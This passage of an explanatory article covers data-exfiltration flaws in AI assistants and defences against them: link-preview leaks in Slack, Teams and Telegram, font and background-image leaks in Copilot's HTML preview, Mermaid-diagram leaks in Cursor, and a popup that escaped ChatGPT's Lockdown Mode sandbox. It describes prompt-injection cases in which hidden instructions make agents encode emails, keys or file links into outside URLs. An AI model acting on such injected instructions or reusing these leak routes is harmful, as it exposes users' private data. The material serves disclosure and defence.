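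Teams with Copilot Studio produced the largest share of the recorded requests, which Wondrasek attributes to the number of companies using it. The share is therefore weak evidence of how dangerous that combination is compared with the others. Volunteers chose what to test and used their own settings, so a "safer" result could reflect one person's configuration. The test also recorded only whether an app fetched a link that an agent had posted. An attacker would first need an injection that worked on that agent.

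Wondrasek illustrates PromptArmor's Teams result with the steps of EchoLeak, a different attack that Microsoft has fixed. EchoLeak used the Teams preview service to relay a request for an image on Copilot's own page. In PromptArmor's test, the agent posts an ordinary link in a chat, and the messaging service fetches it to generate a preview, as it does with any link.

### Switching previews off

Slack lets the software that posts a message decide whether Slack may preview its links. By default Slack previews all of them, whether a person or a program posted the message. Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* recommends that developers add two settings to every message their agent posts:

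```
"unfurl_links": false,
"unfurl_media": false
```

Slack then shows the link without contacting the site. Dana can still leak the code by clicking the link, so the settings only prevent the leak from happening without a click. They also apply to one message at a time, so if she copied the answer into a message to a colleague, Slack would treat the link as hers and could fetch it.

Users lose little, because previews still work in messages between people. But developers have to remember to apply the settings everywhere the agent's code posts a message, much as every ChatGPT app had to use url_safe.

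OpenClaw has a similar setting for Telegram, `linkPreview`, which a user can set to `false` in a configuration file. PromptArmor reports that its test site stopped receiving data after this change. But users will only look for the setting if they know about the risk, which PromptArmor calls largely unrecognised.

### Who should prevent the leak

PromptArmor asks messaging services to give developers control over link previews, and asks developers to use that control or pass the choice on to users. Apostol, in *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews*, reports that PromptArmor puts the responsibility largely on the messaging services, which overstates what PromptArmor wrote.

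Developers are the obvious people to act first, because their software can identify which messages a model wrote. In Slack, they can turn off link previews with two lines of code. Even Anthropic missed this in a connector that let AI agents post to Slack, published as an example when it introduced the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard way of linking models to other software. The connector left previews on, so a hijacked agent could leak data by posting a link.

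The public vulnerability catalogue lists the flaw as CVE-2025-34072. NIST's *CVE-2025-34072 Detail* describes it as a vulnerability in Anthropic's connector, although Slack's preview programs make the requests. *CVE-2025-34072* (2025), from Spain's cybersecurity institute INCIBE, is dated 2 July 2025 and rates the flaw's severity at 9.3 out of 10.

By then Anthropic had stopped maintaining the connector, but other people were still using it. Embrace The Red's *Security Advisory* recommends that anyone who runs or distributes it assess the risk and apply a patch themselves. A company whose employee installed the connector a year ago would have to do this too, even though it is reasonable to blame the developer.

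The messaging service could protect that company by turning off previews of links from programs by default and letting developers turn them on. A bot that posts news stories would lose its previews until somebody changed a setting, but that is a minor inconvenience compared with protecting every agent whose developer forgot to turn previews off. Some developers would no doubt switch previews back on without considering the risk. PromptArmor suggests the more limited change of allowing different preview settings for each chat or channel. A company could then keep previews for its staff and switch them off wherever an agent posts.

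Such a setting would also help administrators. At present they can review which agents have access to the company's chats, but they can't configure an agent they don't know about. Wondrasek describes a developer who connects OpenClaw to a work Slack account without telling anyone.

Microsoft makes the agent Copilot Cowork as well as Teams and Outlook, so responsibility is split among fewer companies. According to Microsoft's documentation, Cowork asks for permission before sending an email or posting in Teams. PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* found that it did not ask when the recipient was the user, and that users could not change this. These messages can still leak data, because Teams and Outlook load outside images when the user opens them.

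PromptArmor hid five lines of instructions in an 81-line skill file, which tells Cowork how to do a particular kind of task. When the user asked for a review of the week's work, Cowork collected download links to the user's files and put them into image addresses in a Teams message. Opening the message sent the links to the attacker, who could then download the files without signing in. The attack worked in all five trials. Cowork's window showed that it had posted to Teams but did not show the message, so a user checking there would not have seen the images.

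The images loaded in Teams, so a sanitiser in Cowork's window would not have stopped them. Microsoft could have required approval for these messages too, or removed outside images from anything Cowork sends. Administrators can block downloads from chosen SharePoint sites, which stops Cowork from obtaining the links, but employees then can't print or sync the files or open them in Word or Excel.

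## HTML previews, stylesheets and diagrams inside the chat

Copilot Cowork's images leaked data because Teams displayed what the model had written. Many assistants now also have renderers in the chat window itself besides the one for ordinary answers, such as a preview for web pages written by the model, a canvas that runs small programs, or a tool that draws diagrams. Each of these may load files from outside addresses.

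Suppose Dana asks her assistant to turn the price list into a web page. The model writes the HTML in a code block, which a markdown sanitiser leaves unchanged. When a preview renders that code as a live page, the browser requests every file the page needs, even though the sanitiser worked as intended.

A page can request files without containing any image tags. Its stylesheet, which sets the colours, fonts and layout, might include these lines (without the usual prefixes):

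```
body { background-image: url(pictures.example/paper.png) }

@font-face { font-family: Headline;
             src: url(fonts.example/headline.woff2) }

h1   { font-family: Headline }
```

The `body` rule puts a picture behind the text. The `@font-face` rule gives the address of a font called Headline, which the browser downloads because the `h1` rule uses it for the main heading. The server hosting each file receives that file's full address, so a door code in either address would leak.

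### Microsoft 365 Copilot's HTML preview

Rehberger found a leak of this kind in Microsoft 365 Copilot in autumn 2025, and Microsoft catalogued the flaw as CVE-2026-24299. Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON*, based on his talk at a hacker conference in Singapore, describes it.

He found the preview while looking for new tools in Copilot. One tool had the same name as a ChatGPT tool for creating documents, so he tested whether Copilot could display HTML. It could, but through a separate feature that showed web pages inside the chat.

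Rehberger asked for a page with a heading and an image from his own server. The preview showed the heading but not the image, because it removed image tags. The feature also showed the page's code by default, so a user had to switch to the preview before the browser loaded anything.

He then asked Copilot to write a page that loaded outside resources in as many ways as it could. One of them, a background image named in a stylesheet, got past the filter. Microsoft had blocked the most familiar way to load a picture but not the network request itself. Any attacker could have asked a language model to do the same, so finding the gap did not require an expert.

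The browser still checked the background image against the CSP of the page that contained Copilot. Copilot appeared in its own chat site, SharePoint and the web version of Excel, each with a different CSP, so the same answer could leak data in one product but not in another.

The lists of allowed image sources were also long. Rehberger noticed subdomains of azureedge.net, where Microsoft's cloud customers could have their own addresses. Microsoft was retiring the domain, but customers still controlled many of those addresses. Other entries belonged to test versions of Microsoft's services, and some contained what looked like employees' usernames, so he suspected that individual employees had added their own domains. He concluded that Microsoft did not control the lists tightly and that a CSP was not a reliable barrier in Copilot.

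Rehberger considered mapping each host's CSP to find a way around it, but he didn't need to because the CSPs restricted fonts even less than images. In many of the applications that included Copilot, the browser could request a font from his own server. The request alone leaks the data, but whoever wrote those rules may have regarded fonts as harmless because a font file cannot read anything on the page.

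The user still had to open the preview. Rehberger removed this step by telling Copilot in his hidden instructions to show the preview, which it reliably did. The default view was only a convenience setting that Microsoft had let the model change.

In one demonstration, the user opened a shared Word document and typed "hi there" to Copilot. Instructions in the document made Copilot search the user's mailbox for an email with the subject "The Code", put its contents into a font address and open the preview. When the browser requested the font, Rehberger's server received the email. He demonstrated the attack in the desktop and web versions of Word and in Excel.

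He also combined the leak with Copilot's memory, much as he had with ChatGPT in SpAIware, so that later conversations leaked passwords and codes. Microsoft reported a fix for the memory part on 6 December 2025.

The preview took longer to fix:

| Date | Event |
|---|---|
| 16 October 2025 | Rehberger reports the background images and fonts |
| 20 October | He realises that the CSP depends on where Copilot is embedded |
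| 12 November | Microsoft confirms that it can reproduce the leak |
| 17 December | Microsoft pays a reward |
| 25 February 2026 | Microsoft is rolling out a fix |
| 5 March | Microsoft marks the report as resolved |

The process took 20 weeks. Embrace The Red does not describe the fix. If Microsoft only added fonts and background images to the list of things the preview removes, someone may find another way to load a file. A rule that stopped the preview from contacting any outside server would be much harder to get around.

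Rehberger suggests that Microsoft also adopt an address check like OpenAI's and Google's. He did not think Copilot had one. Such a check would have blocked a font address containing an email, but only if Microsoft had applied it to the preview's requests as well as to links and images in ordinary answers.

### Who secures an embedded assistant

Rehberger sees a broader problem with AI widgets, his term for assistants that a vendor designs for other websites or programs to embed. The vendor may rely on the surrounding page's CSP to stop leaks, while the page's owner assumes that the assistant is safe by itself. He argues that they need an explicit security contract, with documentation that states who is responsible for preventing data theft.

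Suppose a hotel chain adds a booking assistant to its website. The assistant's maker tested it on a page whose CSP allowed images and fonts only from the maker's own servers. The hotel's page has a CSP that allows them from dozens of advertising and analytics companies, or has no CSP. The same code now runs without the protection it had in testing, and the hotel can't tell this from looking at the screen.

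The problem occurred even though Microsoft made both Copilot and the programs around it. It should be harder to avoid when the companies are separate, because the assistant's maker can't correct the hotel's CSP. Documentation would help the customers who read it, but it would be safer for the maker to build the protection into the assistant, so that customers get it without doing anything.

### Mermaid diagrams in Cursor and Microsoft 365 Copilot

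Diagram tools had caused similar leaks earlier in 2025. Mermaid is a notation that lets people, or language models, describe a diagram in text:

```
graph TD
  Order --> Delivery
  Delivery --> Invoice
```

Mermaid turns the text in a code block into a diagram, such as three boxes joined by arrows. A markdown parser treats the block like any other code block, but Mermaid also lets a box contain HTML, including an image tag.

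The code editor Cursor displayed Mermaid diagrams in its chat. Rehberger found that if a diagram included an image from his server, Cursor loaded it without asking the user. Embrace The Red's *Cursor IDE* describes two attacks that used this. Each began when a developer asked Cursor to explain a source file that had instructions hidden in a comment. In one, Cursor searched the project for secret keys and put them in the address of an image inside a diagram. In the other, it leaked information it had stored about the developer.

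As a normal answer streams in, the user may see a long URL full of data. Here the diagram appeared already finished, so the developer had no chance to notice the data being sent.

Rehberger reported the flaw, CVE-2025-54132, on 30 June 2025. Cursor's maker resolved it within a week and included the fix in version 1.3, available from 29 July. But on 3 October, GCVE's *CVE-2025-61589* (2025) recorded another leak through images in Mermaid diagrams, in all versions up to 1.6. The security company SentinelOne's *CVE-2025-61589* lists version 1.7 as the fix. Either the original fix missed a way of putting an image into a diagram, or a later version of Cursor undid it.

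Adam Logue found a different way to use Mermaid to leak data from Microsoft 365 Copilot. According to daily.dev's *Microsoft 365 Copilot Arbitrary Data Exfiltration Via Mermaid Diagrams*, which summarizes his post, hidden instructions in an Excel document made Copilot fetch the user's recent emails and encode them in hexadecimal. Copilot then drew a diagram styled as a login button, which linked to an address containing the encoded emails.

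Red Hot Cyber's *A serious bug in Microsoft 365 Copilot leads to data exfiltration* (2025) confirms that this leak required one click. But office workers see login buttons every day and expect to log in to see a protected document, so they have a good reason to click. A warning about suspicious links might not make them think of a button in Copilot's own window.

Microsoft responded by removing the ability to interact with dynamic content in the diagrams, so clicking the button no longer did anything. Users can still see the diagrams. Logue received no reward because Microsoft's reward programme did not cover Microsoft 365 Copilot at the time. Microsoft's payment to Rehberger in December suggests that it had since added Copilot to the programme.

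### What Lockdown Mode restricts

OpenAI offers a setting in ChatGPT that restricts many of these features together. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) describes the restrictions as deterministic. OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*, the help page for the setting, lists what it changes:

| Feature | With Lockdown Mode on | What remains |
|---|---|---|
| Images | ChatGPT may not show them in ordinary answers or retrieve them from the web | Uploading and generating images |
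| Web browsing | Limited to stored copies of pages | Search, with results that may be missing or out of date |
| Deep Research and Agent Mode | Off | Ordinary chat |
| Canvas | Users can't let its programs use the network | Programs that don't need the network |
| File downloads | ChatGPT can't download files to analyse them | Analysing files the user uploads |
| Connected apps, personal accounts | No live access or changes that conflict with the protections | Uses that don't conflict |
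| Connected apps, managed workspaces | The administrator chooses which apps and actions to allow | Whatever the administrator allows |

The public-index check still lets the owner of a group of indexed pages see which ones ChatGPT chooses. Limiting browsing to stored copies prevents this because, according to OpenAI, no live request then leaves the company's network.

The help page gives no separate rule for links. ChatGPT's usual check on addresses presumably still applies, since OpenAI says Lockdown Mode builds on its existing protections against leaks through URLs. But if Dana clicks a link and ignores the warning, her browser makes the request, so a limit on OpenAI's servers can't stop it.

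OpenAI advises administrators not to let a connected app make changes unless they are sure that an attacker can't see them. For example, if ChatGPT can comment on a public page, an attacker could read private data in a comment without receiving a web request. OpenAI sees less risk of data leaking when ChatGPT reads from a trusted app, although the app may contain data that an attacker wants.

OpenAI first offered Lockdown Mode on 13 February 2026 to organisations using ChatGPT Enterprise, ChatGPT Edu, ChatGPT for Healthcare and ChatGPT for Teachers. Administrators in those organisations assign it to particular people. On 4 June, OpenAI began extending it to personal accounts and self-managed business accounts. The personal accounts included free ones, according to the announcement Willison quotes. Whether someone can use it still depends on their account and their administrator's settings.

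Users with personal or self-managed business accounts can turn the mode on in their security settings and turn it off for a single chat. The per-chat option is convenient, but an attacker could use a hijacked answer to try to persuade the user that a task requires turning the mode off. The mode does not affect network access in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. Developers control that access through a separate setting, which OpenAI labels "Elevated Risk".

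OpenAI warns that some risk of leaks may remain in this mode because of enabled apps, new techniques and "unforeseen combinations of capabilities". An example soon appeared in a preview of web pages.

### A popup that escaped the preview

In February 2026, OpenAI introduced Lockdown Mode and added an HTML preview for code blocks to ChatGPT. Alexey Bukhteyev, a researcher at the security company Check Point, later found that a page in this preview could bypass Lockdown Mode. *Check Point Bypassed ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode With a Popup* (Duggan, 2026) summarises his report in detail.

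The preview put the generated page inside two nested frames (pages embedded in another page). The browser sandboxed both frames, isolating them and restricting what they could do. According to TechRadar's *AI security controls are only as strong as the wider application environment*, the page could not directly read ChatGPT's cookies or the data ChatGPT stored in the browser. If the page tried to contact an outside server, ChatGPT asked the user for approval.

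This resembles the sandbox that OpenAI described in March for Canvas and ChatGPT Apps. In the same post, OpenAI said it aimed to keep potentially sensitive information from being sent silently. Asking the user for permission allows generated pages that need live data, such as a delivery tracker, to work when a complete block would break them. But asking works only if the software detects every attempt to communicate.

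A page in ChatGPT's preview could open a popup window without the approval ChatGPT normally required. Web pages usually open popups with the browser function `window.open`, which ChatGPT had replaced in the preview with a version that asked for approval. However, a page can create another frame inside itself, and the new frame comes with a fresh copy of the original function, which the page could use to open a window.

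The sandbox's settings allowed popups and exempted them from its restrictions, so the new window could contact any server, even with Lockdown Mode on. The browser would have refused to open the window if the sandbox had prohibited popups.

The consequences were worst in ChatGPT Classic, the older desktop app, where a popup could open without a click. A malicious custom GPT could therefore send the whole chat history to an attacker while the user talked to it. *Même avec son mode de verrouillage activé, ChatGPT laissait fuiter des conversations* (Loupia, 2026) also reports that the leak in this app needed no click. The instructions could also come from a malicious prompt or a shared chat.

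Check Point showed that an attacker could use the same flaw for other kinds of fraud. The popup in the desktop app had ChatGPT's icon and a title the attacker chose, so it could pass for an official update and offer the user malware. The attacker could also sign the user out of the app and display a fake login page.

OpenAI told Check Point on 18 September that it had removed both popup permissions from the outer frame. Check Point retested the attack, and it no longer worked. OpenAI made the change on its servers, so users didn't have to install anything. Check Point published its findings on 5 November and described no real attacks, though Duggan notes that nobody outside OpenAI knows how long the permissions had been in place.

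The original protection failed because ChatGPT's replacement function ran inside the preview, where the attacker's page could get around it. The fix relies on sandbox settings outside the page. The browser enforces these whatever the page's code does. A page can still find an original copy of `window.open`, but calling it no longer opens a window.

OpenAI lists the features that Lockdown Mode restricts, much as Microsoft lists forbidden tags. OpenAI's list includes Canvas but not the HTML preview.

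A week before Check Point's disclosure, Parameter Labs had described another flaw in the same preview. According to The Hacker News, an attacker could publish a ChatGPT conversation containing a malicious page and send the link to a victim. When the preview opened, the page's code ran as part of chatgpt.com with the victim's login and could take over the account. The victim normally had to click the preview once, but the preview opened automatically if the code block was marked as previewable. Check Point told The Hacker News that the two flaws were different. Check Point's popup escaped from the sandbox into a new window, while Parameter Labs' code could make requests to ChatGPT on the victim's behalf.

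### One network rule for the whole preview

A vendor can avoid listing every dangerous tag by prohibiting all outside files and then allowing only what the preview needs. For example, it could send this CSP with the preview:

```
Content-Security-Policy: default-src 'none';
                         style-src 'unsafe-inline';
                         script-src 'unsafe-inline';
                         img-src data:;
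                         font-src data:
```

`default-src 'none'` blocks every type of file that has no rule of its own, such as video and sound. The next two lines allow styles and scripts written in the page itself. The setting is labelled "unsafe" because on an ordinary site it could let an attacker's code run, but running generated code is the purpose of a preview. The last two lines allow images and fonts only if they are embedded in the page.

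If Dana's hijacked assistant put the door code in a font's URL, the browser would refuse the request. It would do the same for a background image, or for an image in a Mermaid diagram drawn inside the preview. This would work even if the vendor's programmers did not know that stylesheets can load fonts or that diagrams can contain HTML.

The browser also checks addresses that did not exist when the sanitiser examined the code. A script in the page can assemble an address from fragments after the page opens, much as Rehberger had the model in Colab join fragments of text. No search of the code can reliably find such an address, but the browser needs the complete address to make the request.

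Blocking network requests prevents generated pages from showing photos from the web or loading the public code libraries that many pages use to draw charts. A vendor could include its own copies of the most popular libraries in the preview. It could also let users approve other requests, as OpenAI does, which restores more features but relies on people to judge what a page is sending and where.

`default-src` covers the files a page loads but not the windows it opens or the forms it submits. The vendor has to block popups and form submissions in the sandbox settings, as OpenAI did for popups in September. The vendor also needs a rule for links, because the browser would treat a click on Logue's fake login button as an ordinary visit to another page. It could disable links in the preview or send each one through the check it uses for links in the chat.

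These protections also have to apply wherever the preview appears. If Copilot writes the preview directly into the Word or Excel page, the browser uses that page's CSP, so Microsoft has to keep the CSP of every host app equally strict. If Copilot loads the preview in a separate frame from a Microsoft address, Microsoft can send the strict CSP with the frame. Excel's page could then allow fonts from anywhere, but the preview could not load them.
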